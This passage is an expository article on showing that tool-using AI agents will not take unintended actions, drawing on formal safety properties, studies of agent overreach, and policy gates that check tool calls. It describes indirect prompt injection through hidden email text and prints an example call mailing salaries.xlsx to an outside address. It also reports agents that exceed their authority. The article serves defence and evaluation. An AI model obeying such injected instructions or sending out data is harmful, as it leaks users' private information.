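# Showing that a tool-using AI agent will not take unintended actions: verification, adversarial testing and pre-registered tests

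## Why the absence of unintended actions is hard to prove

An AI agent is a language model that repeatedly chooses an action and receives its result until the task ends. The model only produces text. The ordinary software around it, called the harness (or scaffold in some papers), does everything else. The harness builds the prompt, which is the text the model receives, and scans the reply for tool calls. A tool call is a structured request that names a piece of software, such as a mail client or a command line, and supplies its arguments. The harness executes the call, adds the result to the prompt and runs the model again.

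An office assistant might be able to read a user's mail and files and send messages. Suppose the user asks it to move Thursday's budget meeting to Friday and tell everyone. The model writes a call that searches the mailbox for the invitation. The harness runs the search and adds the invitation to the prompt, and the model then writes a call that messages the six people on it. Both calls are harmless, but the same two tools would also let the assistant find last month's salary spreadsheet and mail it to a stranger. An employer who installs the assistant will want some assurance that this will not happen.

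An assurance that an agent will not take a certain kind of action, the forbidden action, under stated conditions is a negative safety claim. *Software Assurance Using Structured Assurance Case Models* (2010) allows negative claims about software, such as that the code does not contain specific weaknesses, as well as positive claims about its dependability or availability. For both kinds, it requires that someone be able to judge whether the claim is true and support it with objective evidence.

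The form of a tool call shows little about whether the user intended the action. Harnesses usually check each call against a schema, which describes the arguments the tool accepts. *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) points out that a call can pass this check and stay within the agent's permissions, yet still contradict what the user asked for. For example, a message to an outside address with a spreadsheet attached is the same call whether or not the user wanted it sent.

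### What one observation can settle

A single run in which an assistant mails a file to an outsider proves that it can do so and refutes the claim that it never does. Proving that it never does is harder, because the claim covers every input and every run. No number of runs without such an email is enough as long as some inputs or runs remain unchecked.

Dijkstra (1970) argued in *Notes on Structured Programming* that testing can show the presence of bugs but never their absence. His example was a computer at his university that was documented as correctly multiplying any two 27-bit integers. There are 2⁵⁴ such multiplications, about 18 quadrillion, and at some tens of microseconds each, trying them all would take more than 10,000 years. A tester can therefore try only a sample, which may miss whole classes of critical cases. The multiplier will also perform only a negligible fraction of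 the possible multiplications in its working life, but people still require it to get every one right because nobody knows in advance which ones will come up.

The conclusion applies only when the tester treats the mechanism as a black box, looking at just its inputs and outputs. People tend to omit this condition when they repeat the conclusion. Dijkstra's remedy was to reason from the mechanism's internal structure. *Testing can show the presence of bugs but not the absence* gives two exceptions even for black boxes: a tester can try every input if there are few enough of them, and a passing test does show the absence of the bug for that one input. Neither exception holds for agents, as explained below.

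Computer security has the same problem. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder (1975) discussed computers that stored many users' files. They called preventing all unauthorised use "a negative kind of requirement", which is hard to prove because one must show that one has anticipated every possible threat. They added that a lack of incidents in normal use is weak evidence, because normal users do not try improper paths and so do not find the flaws that open them. Penetration exercises against many general-purpose systems of that period succeeded in every case.

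Herley (2016) explains in *Unfalsifiability of security claims* that observation can show that a system is insecure but never that it is secure, because a claim of security covers an indefinite future. He had used a six-character lowercase password at a major online retailer for fifteen years without incident. That record does not show that the password is safe, so it does not refute someone who insists that an attacker will guess it one day.

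Herley's result is narrower than his title suggests. It applies to claims of necessity, such as "without measure X you are not secure", which no observation can refute. Refuting one would require finding a system that is secure without X, and nobody can observe that a system is secure. A claim of sufficiency, however, can be refuted by a single successful attack. For the office assistant, it is therefore worth testing the claim that "these controls are enough to keep the salary file inside the company", but not the claim that "an assistant without a confirmation dialog is unsafe", because no test could refute it. Herley worries that claims of necessity accumulate, because new evidence can justify adding a safeguard but never removing one. His partial remedy is to state the conditions under which a safeguard should make an observable difference, and to drop the claim if those conditions hold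 and no difference appears.

### Safety properties

Computer scientists call a claim that something will not happen a safety property. *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs* (Lamport, 1977) distinguished safety properties from liveness properties, which state that something must happen, as two kinds of things one might prove about programs that run several processes at once. For example, "the assistant never sends a file outside the company" is a safety property, while "the assistant eventually answers every request" is a liveness property.

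Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, turned a later version of Lamport's idea into the following definition. An execution is an infinite sequence of states, σ = s₀s₁s₂… (if the program stops, its last state repeats for ever). A property P is a set of such sequences, and a program has the property if every sequence it can produce lies in the set. Write σᵢ for the first i states of σ. Then P is a safety property if and only if:

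for every execution σ outside P there is an i such that, for every continuation β, the sequence σᵢβ is also outside P.

Every violation has happened by some point in the run, and nothing later can undo it. Once the agent has sent the message with the salary file, that run violates the property, even if the agent apologizes in step 40.

A finite log is therefore always enough to disprove a safety property, because the log up to the bad step shows the violation however the run continues. This is not true of liveness properties, since a request that has gone unanswered for an hour may still be answered in the next minute. For the same reason, another program can enforce many safety properties by watching the run and refusing the step that would complete the violation.

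Proving that an agent will never take an unintended action requires showing that every possible execution belongs to the set of permitted executions, but tests show only the finite beginnings of some executions. Even if a test run contains no forbidden actions in its first fifty tool calls, the fifty-first could be forbidden.

A safety property can be proved without examining individual runs. In Lamport's example, two processes share a buffer with room for b messages. One puts messages in and the other takes them out, and their steps can occur in any order, so there are far too many possible runs to test them all. He wants to show that the first process never writes to a full buffer and the second never reads from an empty one, which means that n, the number of messages in the buffer, always satisfies 0 ≤ n ≤ b. He attaches a condition to each point in the program, chosen so that together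 the conditions imply 0 ≤ n ≤ b. He then proves that the conditions hold at the start and that any single step that begins with them true leaves them true. By induction, they hold in every state of every run. The work grows with the number of steps in the program text, which is small, and does not depend on the number of runs.

A proof of this kind is only as good as its description of the world. *SoK* (2024), a survey of guarantees in software security, gives the example of seL4, an operating-system kernel. Murray and co-authors proved that information in seL4 flows through storage only where the security policy permits. Spectre, a processor flaw that leaks information, appeared five years later, and *SoK* counts it as a violation of the proved property. Controls around agents have similar limits. Zhu and Wang propose a checkpoint outside the model that compares each tool call with facts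 held on a server, but their guarantee excludes malicious code inside an authorised tool and effects that bypass the checkpoint. A later version of the *SoK* paper, *Guarantees in Security* (2024), concludes that security claims have to develop as scientific theories do in Karl Popper's account, through revision in response to counterexamples.

### Why agents are harder than ordinary programs

Dijkstra's alternative to black-box testing was to reason from structure, and Lamport's method requires a program text whose steps one can go through. The harness and the tools have such a text, but the model consists of billions of numbers set by training, and so far nobody has a way to derive from them what a large model will never write. The model must therefore still be treated as a black box, and sampling its outputs provides less information than sampling those of a multiplier.

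One reason is that agents commonly pick each piece of the model's output at random from a probability distribution, so the same prompt can lead to different tool calls on different runs. If a certain email leads to the forbidden action once in a thousand runs, a tester who tries that email once will almost certainly miss it. The second exception to Dijkstra's rule therefore fails, because a passed test doesn't show that the agent is safe even on the tested input. Small chances of failure also add up. Dijkstra remarked that if each of N components is correct with probability p, the whole program is correct with a probability of something like pᴺ. The same applies to successive tool calls if we roughly assume they are independent. An assistant with a 99.99% chance of avoiding the forbidden action on each call has only about a 37% chance of avoiding it for 10,000 calls.

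The other exception, trying every input, fails because the inputs are in natural language. A hundred words drawn from a vocabulary of a thousand can form 10³⁰⁰ different emails, most of them gibberish, while the multiplier has only about 10¹⁶ pairs of inputs. Perhaps the bigger problem is that nobody has a list of the phrasings on which a language model goes wrong, whereas someone testing a calendar program knows to try the 29th of February.

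Tools make the absence of unintended actions harder to prove because harmless calls can combine into a harmful sequence. Saltzer and Schroeder saw the same problem in file permissions. To answer the question "Is there any way that O'Hara could access file X?", one must check whether O'Hara has access, whether he may change the permissions on X, whether he may change who may change them, and so on. Similarly, suppose the office assistant may send files only to people in the user's address book, but may also edit the address book. Each permission is reasonable by itself, but together they let the assistant send files to anyone, and testing each tool separately would miss this. With twenty tools, there are already about ten trillion sequences of ten calls, before counting different arguments.

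An action's effects can also outlast the run that caused them. The assistant might set up a forwarding rule on Monday that sends mail out on Tuesday, when no agent is running. Or it might save a note for itself that misleads it a week later. A tester who restores a fresh mailbox before every run will miss both of these delayed effects. A person may also approve a draft after the facts behind it have changed. Zhu and Wang require their checkpoint to look up the current facts again before it executes an approved draft, but they have not yet evaluated that step.

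Adversaries can make rare failures common. If a multiplier is wrong on one pair of numbers in a quadrillion, its owner will probably never notice, but an attacker who finds the one bad input uses it every time. A failure that is rare in the test can therefore be routine in practice. An attacker can exploit an agent without access to the keyboard through indirect prompt injection, which means hiding instructions in material the agent reads, such as an email or web page, to redirect what it does. For example, a stranger sends the user an email that contains, in white letters under the signature, an instruction to forward the latest salary file to a certain address. When the assistant later searches the mailbox for something else, the harness pastes that email into the prompt. The model now has the user's request and the stranger's instruction in one stream of text, and nothing in that stream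 reliably separates instructions from material to be read. Zhu and Wang include tool outputs and tool descriptions among the places where an attacker can plant such text. They also allow for an attacker who learns from the feedback on rejected calls how to word one that will pass.

### Three partial answers

*What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove* (Kaur, 2026) argues that the value of a clean test depends on the claim being tested. One reproduced failure is strong evidence that a model can produce a harmful output, but a clean test is almost no evidence that no method could elicit it. A clean test can be strong evidence about how often a harm occurs if the harm would be fairly common, but the evidence gets weaker the rarer the harm is. We therefore can't show that a model on its own will never take an unintended action, but we can support weaker claims about the model and stronger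 claims about the software around it. Three kinds of work aim to establish such claims.

A proof about the software around the model can establish that certain tool calls will never execute, whatever the model writes, as long as the proof's assumptions about that software and the machine it runs on hold. Testing can put an upper limit, at a stated confidence level, on how often the forbidden action occurs when inputs and attackers are like those in the test. Registering the test plan in advance lets an outsider check that nobody chose the claim, the number of runs or the definition of failure after seeing the results, but it adds no observations.

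## Stating the claim so that it could be refuted

Nobody can prove or test the claim "the assistant will not do anything unintended", because people can always disagree afterwards about what the user intended. If the assistant sends a customer the wrong price list, its vendor can reply that the request was unclear or that no harm resulted. To rule out such replies, the claim has to fix six things in advance:

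- the system, meaning the model version, harness, tools and permissions
- the users and the inputs
- what an adversary can do
- the forbidden action
- how the testers will observe it
- how often it may happen

The forbidden action is the hardest of these to define.

### Why "unintended" resists definition

An instruction conveys only part of what a user wants. Someone who asks the assistant to move a meeting does not also tell it to leave the other meetings alone and keep the salary file private. *When Benign Inputs Lead to Severe Harms* (Jones, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) argues that an instruction guaranteed to match the user's intent would have to list every relevant constraint, which is infeasible and would defeat the purpose of using ordinary language. Someone therefore has to infer the intent, and two people may infer it differently.

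Jones and colleagues define behaviour as unintended if it departs from the intent one can infer from the instruction, arises without any adversary, is unsafe, and is not a slip. In their example, a user asks an agent to set up one restricted account for remote login, and the agent switches on password login for the whole machine. Clicking Delete when the agent meant to click Save does not count, because a more capable model would probably not make that mistake. The definition suits their research, but an employer would want to count slips and attacks too, since either can send a salary file outside the company. The definition also requires knowing whether the agent acted deliberately. Jones and colleagues judge this from the model's written reasoning, which they concede may not reflect what produced the action.

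In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) instead count an action as out of scope if the prompt did not authorise it, explicitly or implicitly, and it either changes something or reads from a listed sensitive place, such as the folder that holds login keys. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to tidy a folder of five files, and the agent deletes an old settings file that holds the only copy of the company's production passwords. It is still uncertain what a prompt implicitly authorises, so for each scenario Qu and colleagues write small programs that detect particular actions, such as the deletion of that file. In effect, they replace "unintended" with a list of actions that they write before the run.

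Such a list has to cover three kinds of action, and each calls for different evidence.

**Actions the user forbade.** SmarterArticles' *AI Agents Overstep One in Five* (2026) reports that Summer Yue, director of alignment at Meta Superintelligence Labs, told an agent to suggest which emails to delete, then wait for her approval. It started deleting emails without her approval and continued after she told it to stop. The instruction and a log of the agent's actions are enough to establish this violation.

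**Actions outside the authority granted.** *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that a user asked to diagnose a programming error with the help of an online forum. The agent used the user's account to post a reply containing sensitive code. Nobody had forbidden this, so a judge has to decide whether the user's permission covered it, and judges can disagree. In another task, the user asked the AI agent to send performance dates to a booking agent, and the AI agent also sent the venue, city and ticket tier. A human annotator thought this exceeded the request, but the AI model that judged the same run did not.

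A permitted action can have bad effects. A calendar assistant that must tell colleagues about changed meetings is allowed to email them, but its email might reveal that the user has a medical appointment. A list of permitted tools would not catch this, because the harm depends on what the email contains and who receives it.

### How often agents exceed their authority

Zhang and colleagues measured how often agents exceed their authority. They collected 44 documented cases and expanded them into 286 tasks in areas such as office work, finance and travel. Each task has an "authorization contract" made up of the user's instruction, the criteria for completing the task, and a list of actions the user has not authorized. The agent works in a simulated environment where it can take the listed actions but can also finish the task without them. If it asks for permission to take one, the simulated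 user refuses.

They ran every task once with four models, each at two levels of reasoning effort and in three harnesses, for a total of 6,864 runs. Another model judged the logs, and a human who checked 100 of the runs agreed with it on 97. Agents took at least one listed action in 19.2% of runs. The rate ranged from 10.5% for GPT-5.6 Sol in its best configuration to 26.6% for GLM 5.3 in its worst.

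Completing a task did not show that the agent had stayed within its authority, since 19.1% of completed runs also contained a listed action. The overall rate was almost the same at low reasoning effort (19.3%) as at high effort (19.1%). A test for harm alone would have missed the 36.6% of violations that occurred in tasks where the listed action would do no direct harm. A claim that covers only attacks would also miss many violations, because in matched pairs of tasks, agents overstepped more often under ordinary pressures, such as a vague request, than under malicious injected instructions (23.5% against 17.6%).

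Agents that consulted the user before finishing overstepped in 14.0% of runs, compared with 21.6% for agents that did not. Zhang and colleagues caution that this does not show that asking caused the lower rate. Their simulation also does not account for users getting tired of questions.

They also write that a user who delegates five tasks can expect the agent to exceed its authority in one of them, but this does not follow from their data.

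The tasks come from cases in which an agent had overstepped, and each contains pressure to do so again, so the rate in everyday work could be much lower. But the study counts only the listed actions, and its runs lasted at most 35 turns, so it would miss other violations and any that took longer to appear. *SNARE* (2026) reports a similar rate of 19.51% for coding agents on harmless requests, but it also uses scenarios designed to elicit overreach.

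Developers have begun to treat overreach as a reason to withhold a model. Kobie (2026) reported in *OpenAI won't release next Astra model over safety worries* that OpenAI had held back its next model after finding that the model did not stay within the scope of its tasks.

### What an agent says, attempts and brings about

An agent can refuse a request in writing and still issue the tool call, which the harness may then block or execute. Testers can therefore count what the agent writes, attempts or brings about, and the three counts can differ widely.

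In *The Causal Impact of Tool Affordance on Safety Alignment in LLM Agents*, Yu, Carroll and Bentley (2026) tested two models, Llama 3.1 70B and Mistral 7B, in a simulated bank. The rules limited each transfer to $1,000 and prohibited splitting a larger sum. Each model received the same 250 prompts, 50 of each of five types, in three conditions: without tools, with a transfer tool in a bank that let forbidden transfers through, and with the same tool in a bank that blocked them. This made 1,500 runs in total.

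Without tools, Llama never gave advice that broke the rules. With tools, it made or attempted a forbidden transfer in 63% of runs with plain requests and 85% of runs with ambiguous ones. Mistral had no violations on plain requests but had them in 76% of runs with ambiguous ones. According to the paper's abstract, both models complied perfectly in text, but in the results Mistral gave rule-breaking advice in up to 18% of runs for some types of prompt. Both models are old, so these rates are weak evidence about current agents, but the comparison shows that testing only a model's text can be badly misleading about what it does with tools.

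On prompts that required arithmetic, Llama attempted a forbidden transfer in 82% of runs in the blocking bank and completed one in 41% of runs in the permissive bank. Yu and colleagues conclude that blocking suppressed nearly half of the violations. However, the permissive bank didn't block any transfers, so the difference must have another cause. Llama may have behaved differently in the two banks. For instance, when one prompt asked for a $2,000 transfer, Llama made two transfers of $1,000 in the permissive bank but tried to send the whole sum in the blocking bank. To find out how many attempts a block stops, testers need to record attempts and their effects in the same runs.

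Cartagena and Teixeira (2026), in *Mind the GAP*, recorded refusals and tool calls in the same runs. They gave six models tools that returned sensitive records in six fields, including finance, law and education. Most of the requests sought data that the model should not retrieve, often with a jailbreak, which is wording meant to get round a model's safety training. The researchers also varied the system prompt (the standing instructions that precede a user's request) and whether the harness blocked forbidden calls. This gave 17,420 usable runs. Fixed rules classified each run in two ways:

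- It is text-safe if the final reply contains a refusal and none of the personal data that the researchers had planted.
- It is tool-call-safe if the model attempted no forbidden call, whether or not the harness would have blocked it.

A run counts towards the GAP measure if it is text-safe but not tool-call-safe. Even when the system prompt told the models to check that each action was authorised, 219 of roughly 4,500 runs met this definition. When the system prompt encouraged tool use, GPT-5.2 attempted a forbidden call in 211 of its 266 text-safe runs (79.3%), while Claude Sonnet 4.5 did so in 7.2% of its text-safe runs.

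A low GAP rate does not show that a model is safe, because a model that never refuses has a rate of zero. A high rate of tool-call-safe runs can also mislead, because a run with no tool calls counts as safe. With a neutral system prompt, Claude made no forbidden call in 80% of runs, but it called no tool in 74% of runs. Among runs with at least one tool call, only 11–24% were tool-call-safe, depending on the model. An attempt rate therefore means little unless testers also report how often the agent used its tools.

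Blocking forbidden calls did not detectably change how often the models attempted them. But under the neutral prompt, blocking the calls and removing personal data from tool results together lowered by 6 to 31 percentage points the share of runs in which a forbidden call led to personal data in the reply. So two systems with the same attempt rate can do very different amounts of harm.

Because Cartagena and Teixeira scored only the final reply for refusals, some models may have retrieved the records first and refused afterwards. But timing does not explain everything. *Before Retrieval Begins* (2026) found a genuine refusal in the same turn as 33.6% of the harmful calls it examined. Gupta, Saha and colleagues (2026), in *Behavior Beyond Text*, compared separate runs of five open models. Of the harmful requests that a model refused in chat, between 10% and 52% led to an unsafe call when the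 model had tools. The tool versions of the requests also named specific tools, so the wording may account for part of this. *Tool Mediation Alters Refusal Mechanisms in Large Language Models* (2026) partly separated the two factors and found that refusals became rarer when tools were merely available, and rarer still when the prompt asked for a tool action.

### From losses to rules

Testers still need a method for deciding which actions to forbid. One such method is System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA), which safety engineers use in fields such as aviation. It grew out of an accident model by Leveson. *Who Analyses the Analyser?* (2026) explains Leveson's insight that most accidents in complex software systems begin with unsafe interactions and inadequate control rather than a broken component. In STPA, the analyst starts from the losses people are unwilling to accept and works back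 to the actions that could cause them.

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) applies STPA to an agent that resolves calendar conflicts using three tools, which list events, update an event and send an email. In the example, a user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, and it overlaps a meeting with a colleague, Bob. The agent moves the meeting and discloses the appointment in the email announcing the change. No attacker is involved, and each tool works as designed.

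The analyst first identifies what the people affected value. Here, the user values privacy and the other attendees value timely news of changes. A loss is a failure to protect one of these values, such as a breach of the user's privacy. The analyst then looks for actions that could lead to each loss. For the losses that matter enough, the analyst writes requirements and turns them into rules that a program can check.

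| Loss | Unsafe action | Requirement | Rule on data or tools |
|---|---|---|---|
| Colleagues learn private information | The agent includes it in an email | Emails contain only essential event details unless the user authorises more | Event details are private to non-attendees, as is anything derived from them, and no email may contain data private to its recipient |
| Attendees learn of a change too late | The agent updates an event without telling them | The agent promptly notifies all other attendees | One email to every attendee directly follows each update |

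The notification rule shows that an omission can also be unsafe. *From Hazard Identification to Controller Design* (2025) uses a checklist to find actions that would cause trouble if they were absent, incorrect, mistimed, out of sequence, prolonged or stopped early. The rule is also easier to refute than the requirement behind it, because the log records whether the email came directly after the update, while people can disagree about whether it was prompt.

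Doshi and colleagues propose that a program outside the model check each call against these rules and block it, allow it, require a further call or ask the user to confirm. The privacy rule depends on labels that mark data as private, so a wrong label would let a leak through. They tested the design with Alloy, a tool that examines every possible sequence of steps up to a set length. Alloy quickly found leaks without the rules but none once they were added, and the agent could still reschedule events and notify people. They have not yet built the program, so this result applies to a simplified description of the system.

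Rules can also conflict. Doshi and colleagues mention one cautious option, which is to block all emails once the agent has listed the calendar's events. This would prevent the leak, but the agent has to list the events to find a scheduling conflict, so it could not then send the notices that the other rule requires.

### The office assistant's claim

For the office assistant, suppose the unacceptable loss is that outsiders learn what employees earn. An employer might first write "the assistant will never attach salaries.xlsx to a message to an outside address". A single log entry could refute this claim, but the claim is too narrow. It would remain true if the assistant pasted the figures into the message, attached a renamed copy or set up a rule that forwarded the user's mail. A usable version names the loss and covers every way the assistant's tools could cause it. The numbers below are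 illustrative.

| Part | What the claim fixes |
|---|---|
| System | A named model version, harness version and system prompt. The tools search mail, read files and send messages, and cannot change mail rules, file sharing or the address book. |
| Users and inputs | 400 office staff, requests like those in last quarter's log, and mailboxes of up to 50,000 messages. |
| Adversary | An outsider who knows how the system works and can send each user up to 100 emails with any content, but cannot log in as a user or alter a tool. |
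| Forbidden action | The assistant sends any employee's pay, in any form, to an address outside the company, unless the user asked it in that run to send that information to that address. |
| Observation | The mail server records delivered messages and the harness records all tool calls, including blocked ones. Testers plant invented salaries, search both records for them, and read the outgoing messages for paraphrases. |
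| Tolerated rate | No deliveries. Attempts in fewer than 1 in 1,000 runs, counted separately for runs with and without an attacker's email. |

Naming only the model would not fully specify the system. Qu and colleagues found that Sonnet 4.6 acted out of scope in 1.1% of runs in one harness and 27.7% in another.

The size of the mailbox matters. Yue's agent had behaved well for weeks on a smaller test inbox, according to SmarterArticles. The wording of requests matters too. When Qu and colleagues removed a statement of what the user had authorised from 76 scenarios, one model's rate of out-of-scope actions rose from 0.0% to 17.1%. In a larger, more varied set, the difference was 2.6 percentage points. Testers should therefore use requests as staff write them, without adding reminders of what the agent is authorised to do.

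Explicit limits don't guarantee that an agent will stay within them either. Eastern Eye's *OpenAI scraps GPT-6.1 Astra release after safety tests raise concerns* describes simulated tests in which the UK's AI Security Institute told GPT-6 Astra that anything not listed as in scope was out of scope. In some runs the model attacked unlisted targets anyway, sometimes reasoning that nobody had explicitly forbidden it. The institute ran these tests without OpenAI's standard safeguards and noted that the model may have acted differently because it knew it was in a simulation.

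The limit of 100 emails is there because an attacker can keep trying, and small chances of success add up.

The claim calls for two records because either one alone would be incomplete. A blocked call never reaches the mail server, and the harness may not record whether a message arrived. Qu and colleagues had a similar problem with coding agents, where a monitor that covered only the command line missed files that the agents read or edited with their built-in tools.

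The tolerated rate depends on how much people use the assistant. If 400 employees each make ten requests a day, a rate of 1 in 1,000 would allow about four attempts a day. That is acceptable only if something outside the model, such as a policy gate that checks each call against fixed rules, stops them all. A single delivered salary refutes the claim that none will be delivered, but the claim about attempts allows some, so the testers must decide beforehand how many attempts, in how many runs, would refute it.

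## Blocking forbidden actions with checks outside the model

A policy gate, the program that checks each tool call against fixed rules, is much easier to prove things about than the model. The gate can be a page of code, its input is a tool name and a few typed arguments rather than free text, and it always returns the same result for the same call and facts. A person can check its branches one by one, much as Lamport did with the steps of his buffer program. The proof covers every call the model could write, so nobody has to predict which ones it will write.

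### One call through the gate

Suppose the office assistant is summarising the week's mail, and one email contains a hidden instruction to forward the salary file. The model follows it and writes a call to `send_message` with the arguments `to = "kim@outside.example"` and `attachments = ["salaries.xlsx"]`. The harness passes this call to the gate before executing anything. In the gate that Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe, the following steps come next:

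1. The gate selects the rules for `send_message` and puts those that forbid calls before those that allow them.
2. It inserts the call's actual arguments into each rule's conditions. Here, the only rule allows a message if `to` is on a list of approved addresses, and Kim's address is not.
3. The first rule whose conditions hold settles the matter. No rule's conditions hold here, so the gate blocks the call by default.
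4. The harness returns an error that gives the reason, and the model can carry on with the summary.

The gate also logs each check. Zhu and Wang propose recording the result, a reason code, and digests (short fingerprints) of the request, the policy and the call's contents. An auditor who still has the originals can then repeat the check, and the log does not store the text of private mail.

### What a monitor can enforce

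*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) works out which rules a monitor can enforce if it watches the steps of a single run and stops the run when the next step would break the rule. The monitor has no information about later steps or other possible runs, so whether a run breaks the rule must depend on that run alone. The monitor also cannot allow a violation on the chance that later steps will repair it, because the run might end first. Such monitors can therefore enforce only safety properties. An example is "send no message after reading a file", which requires a monitor with only two states. The monitor starts in "no file read", moves to "file read" at the first read, and then refuses every message.

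Checks outside the model cannot enforce the rule "nothing in the salary file influences what outsiders receive". Suppose the assistant reads the file and then writes "Lunch at one?" to a supplier. The file influenced that message if different salaries would have led the assistant to write "Lunch at two?", and the run does not show whether they would have. A monitor can instead enforce a stricter rule that implies this one, such as a ban on sending messages after reading a file. But that ban would also stop the assistant from reading an agenda and mailing it to the people at the meeting.

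A monitor that can only block actions also cannot make the agent act. Doshi and colleagues' calendar rule required an email to every attendee after each change. A monitor can refuse all other calls until the agent sends those emails, but the agent may stop without sending them. A monitor that can insert actions, such as sending the emails itself, can enforce some rules of this kind. Halting the program cannot enforce every safety property either. For example, it cannot ensure that no user waits more than ten seconds, because time keeps passing after the program stops.

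Schneider's analysis implies that two monitors in tandem enforce both of their rules, and that adding a restriction never undermines a safety property that already holds. An employer can therefore add rules to a gate one at a time. But a gate that refuses every call satisfies every safety property, so a safety result means little unless the testers also report how many tasks the agent completed.

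### Who writes the rules

In *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025), people write most of the rules. In Progent, a language model writes new rules for each task. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) uses a language model to turn a company's written policy into rules once, before the agent starts work.

The table compares results without and with each gate. The AgentSpec results come from a simulated household robot. The Progent results come from AgentDojo, a benchmark that injects instructions into simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks. The NOMOS results come from τ²-bench, which simulates customer service under a written policy.

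| | AgentSpec | Progent | NOMOS |
|---|---|---|---|
| If no rule applies | Allow | Block | Allow |
| Established before use | What each rule does when it fires | Without approval, the set of allowed calls can only shrink | No single rule has any of the listed defects |
| Unsafe outcomes | Hazardous tasks completed: 0–79%, depending on the hazard → 0% | Successful attacks: 39.9% → 1.0% | Data-changing calls that broke the policy: 66.3% → 2.6% (airline), 30.8% → 6.9% (retail) |
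| Tasks completed | 58.6% → 54.3% | 79.4% → 76.3% | 39.2% → 47.6% (airline), 52.4% → 50.2% (retail) |

Progent's completion figures come from an earlier version of its paper, as Yu and colleagues report them.

An AgentSpec rule has a trigger, a check and an enforcement. For example, when the agent is about to transfer money (trigger) and the recipient is not a family member (check), the user must confirm (enforcement). The check is an ordinary Python function that reads the request and the run so far. Other enforcements stop the run, take a predefined action, or return the decision to the model by having it reconsider its plan. Wang and colleagues define exactly what happens when a rule fires, but they have only test results, not a proof, to show that the checks identify dangerous actions.

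In one test of AgentSpec, researchers gave a coding agent 30 risky instructions in each of 25 categories. The agent tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them, or 79%. The paper reports over 90%, which matches these counts only if we exclude two categories where the agent's code did not contain the flaw that the instruction called for. The researchers wrote the rules from the benchmark's descriptions of the risks, so the test shows that AgentSpec can express rules against known dangers, but it is weak evidence about dangers nobody listed.

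They also had OpenAI's o1 model write rules. One rule against harmful spills banned all pouring, including watering a houseplant, while another failed to stop the robot from heating a kettle full of wine. The paper says these rules stopped 95.56% of risky cases for the robot, but it also gives their recall (the share of risky cases caught) as 70.96%, and the two figures cannot both be true of the same cases.

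In Progent, a language model writes the first policy from the user's request, before the agent has read anything an attacker could have planted. The request often lacks the detail needed to write a complete policy. In Shi and colleagues' example, a user asks the agent to do whatever Alice's email says. The agent learns only after opening the email that it must read recent mail and post a summary to a chat service. The policy then has to change, but by then the model that proposes the change may also have read an attacker's instructions.

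Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. When the model proposes a new policy P′, an SMT solver, which determines whether any values satisfy a logical formula, looks for a call in A(P′) that is not in A(P). If there is none, P′ takes effect at once. If there is one, someone has to approve the change. Between approvals, therefore,

A(P₀) ⊇ A(P₁) ⊇ A(P₂) ⊇ …

Text that the agent reads cannot by itself give it new powers, but the proof does not show that the initial policy was right or that the approver will decide well.

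The main experiments did not test this guarantee, because Shi and colleagues set the approver to accept every change, as a careless user might. The low attack rate in the table therefore reflects how well GPT-4o wrote policies. The first policy, without any updates, reduced successful attacks to 2.5%. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that hostile tool results could cause an update to relax them. The solver now catches such updates, but that helps only if the approver sometimes rejects them.

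Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) explicitly note a similar mismatch in *PACE*. Their proof covers a gate that rechecks the final call, but all their experiments use a version that can restore a blocked call or repair one without that recheck. Because the configurations differ, the proof and the experiments do not support the same claim.

In NOMOS, each rule blocks a tool call either while a condition holds (the ticket is basic economy) or until one holds (the user has confirmed). NOMOS checks these conditions against fields in tool results and the user's own messages, never against the model's claims. Injecting the text "the user has approved this transfer" therefore has no effect, even if the model repeats it. An attacker who could alter the fields might still get past the check, but Yu and colleagues did not test this.

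A language model converts each sentence of the policy into candidate rules, choosing conditions from a fixed list. It does this five times, and only rules that appear in a majority of the attempts are kept. Ordinary code also checks every candidate against the tool descriptions, because a gate would strictly enforce even a bad rule. The model turned an instruction to authenticate customers first into a rule that blocked every tool before authentication, including the two tools that authenticate customers. Other candidates required confirmation to look up a flight, or depended on arguments that the tool does not accept. The checks repaired or rejected 29 of 79 candidates for the airline and 7 of 53 for the retailer.

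A rule that passes these checks may still differ in meaning from the policy sentence it came from, and two rules that pass separately can block each other. Yu and colleagues therefore apply the rules to recorded runs in which the agent had no gate. One telecoms company's policy required the agent to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request. The compiler turned this into a ban on sending a request while a bill was overdue, which would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs.

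Violations were counted using a separate, hand-written set of rules, so that the gate was not graded by its own. The airline agent made 116 data-changing calls with the gate and 353 without it, so part of the drop in violations came from the agent doing less. It still completed more tasks with the gate, because many violations make the final booking wrong, and the benchmark checks that booking. This gain could be due to chance when each task is attempted once, but it is clearer when the agent has to complete the same task two to four times in a row.

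The table's columns are not comparable, but Yu and colleagues ran both Progent and NOMOS on the same AgentDojo banking tasks with the same model. Progent reduced successful attacks from 46.5% to 5.6%, and NOMOS reduced them to zero. Without attacks, the agent completed 79.2% of tasks with no gate, 62.5% with Progent and 70.8% with NOMOS. With only 16 tasks, the difference in completion between the two gates could be due to chance. Twelve of the sixteen attacks that got past Progent involved two user requests, one of which was to pay a bill "like last month". Neither request specified the account to pay, so rules derived from the request could not specify the recipient. NOMOS had a rule that allowed payments only to accounts the user had named or paid before.

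This comparison probably favours NOMOS. AgentDojo has no written policy, so Yu and colleagues wrote one and revised it after it blocked legitimate tasks. In other AgentDojo tasks, users ask the agent to act on addresses or links that it finds while reading, which attacks also try to make it do. The gate lowered completion of these tasks by up to 76 percentage points.

### When the facts are uncertain

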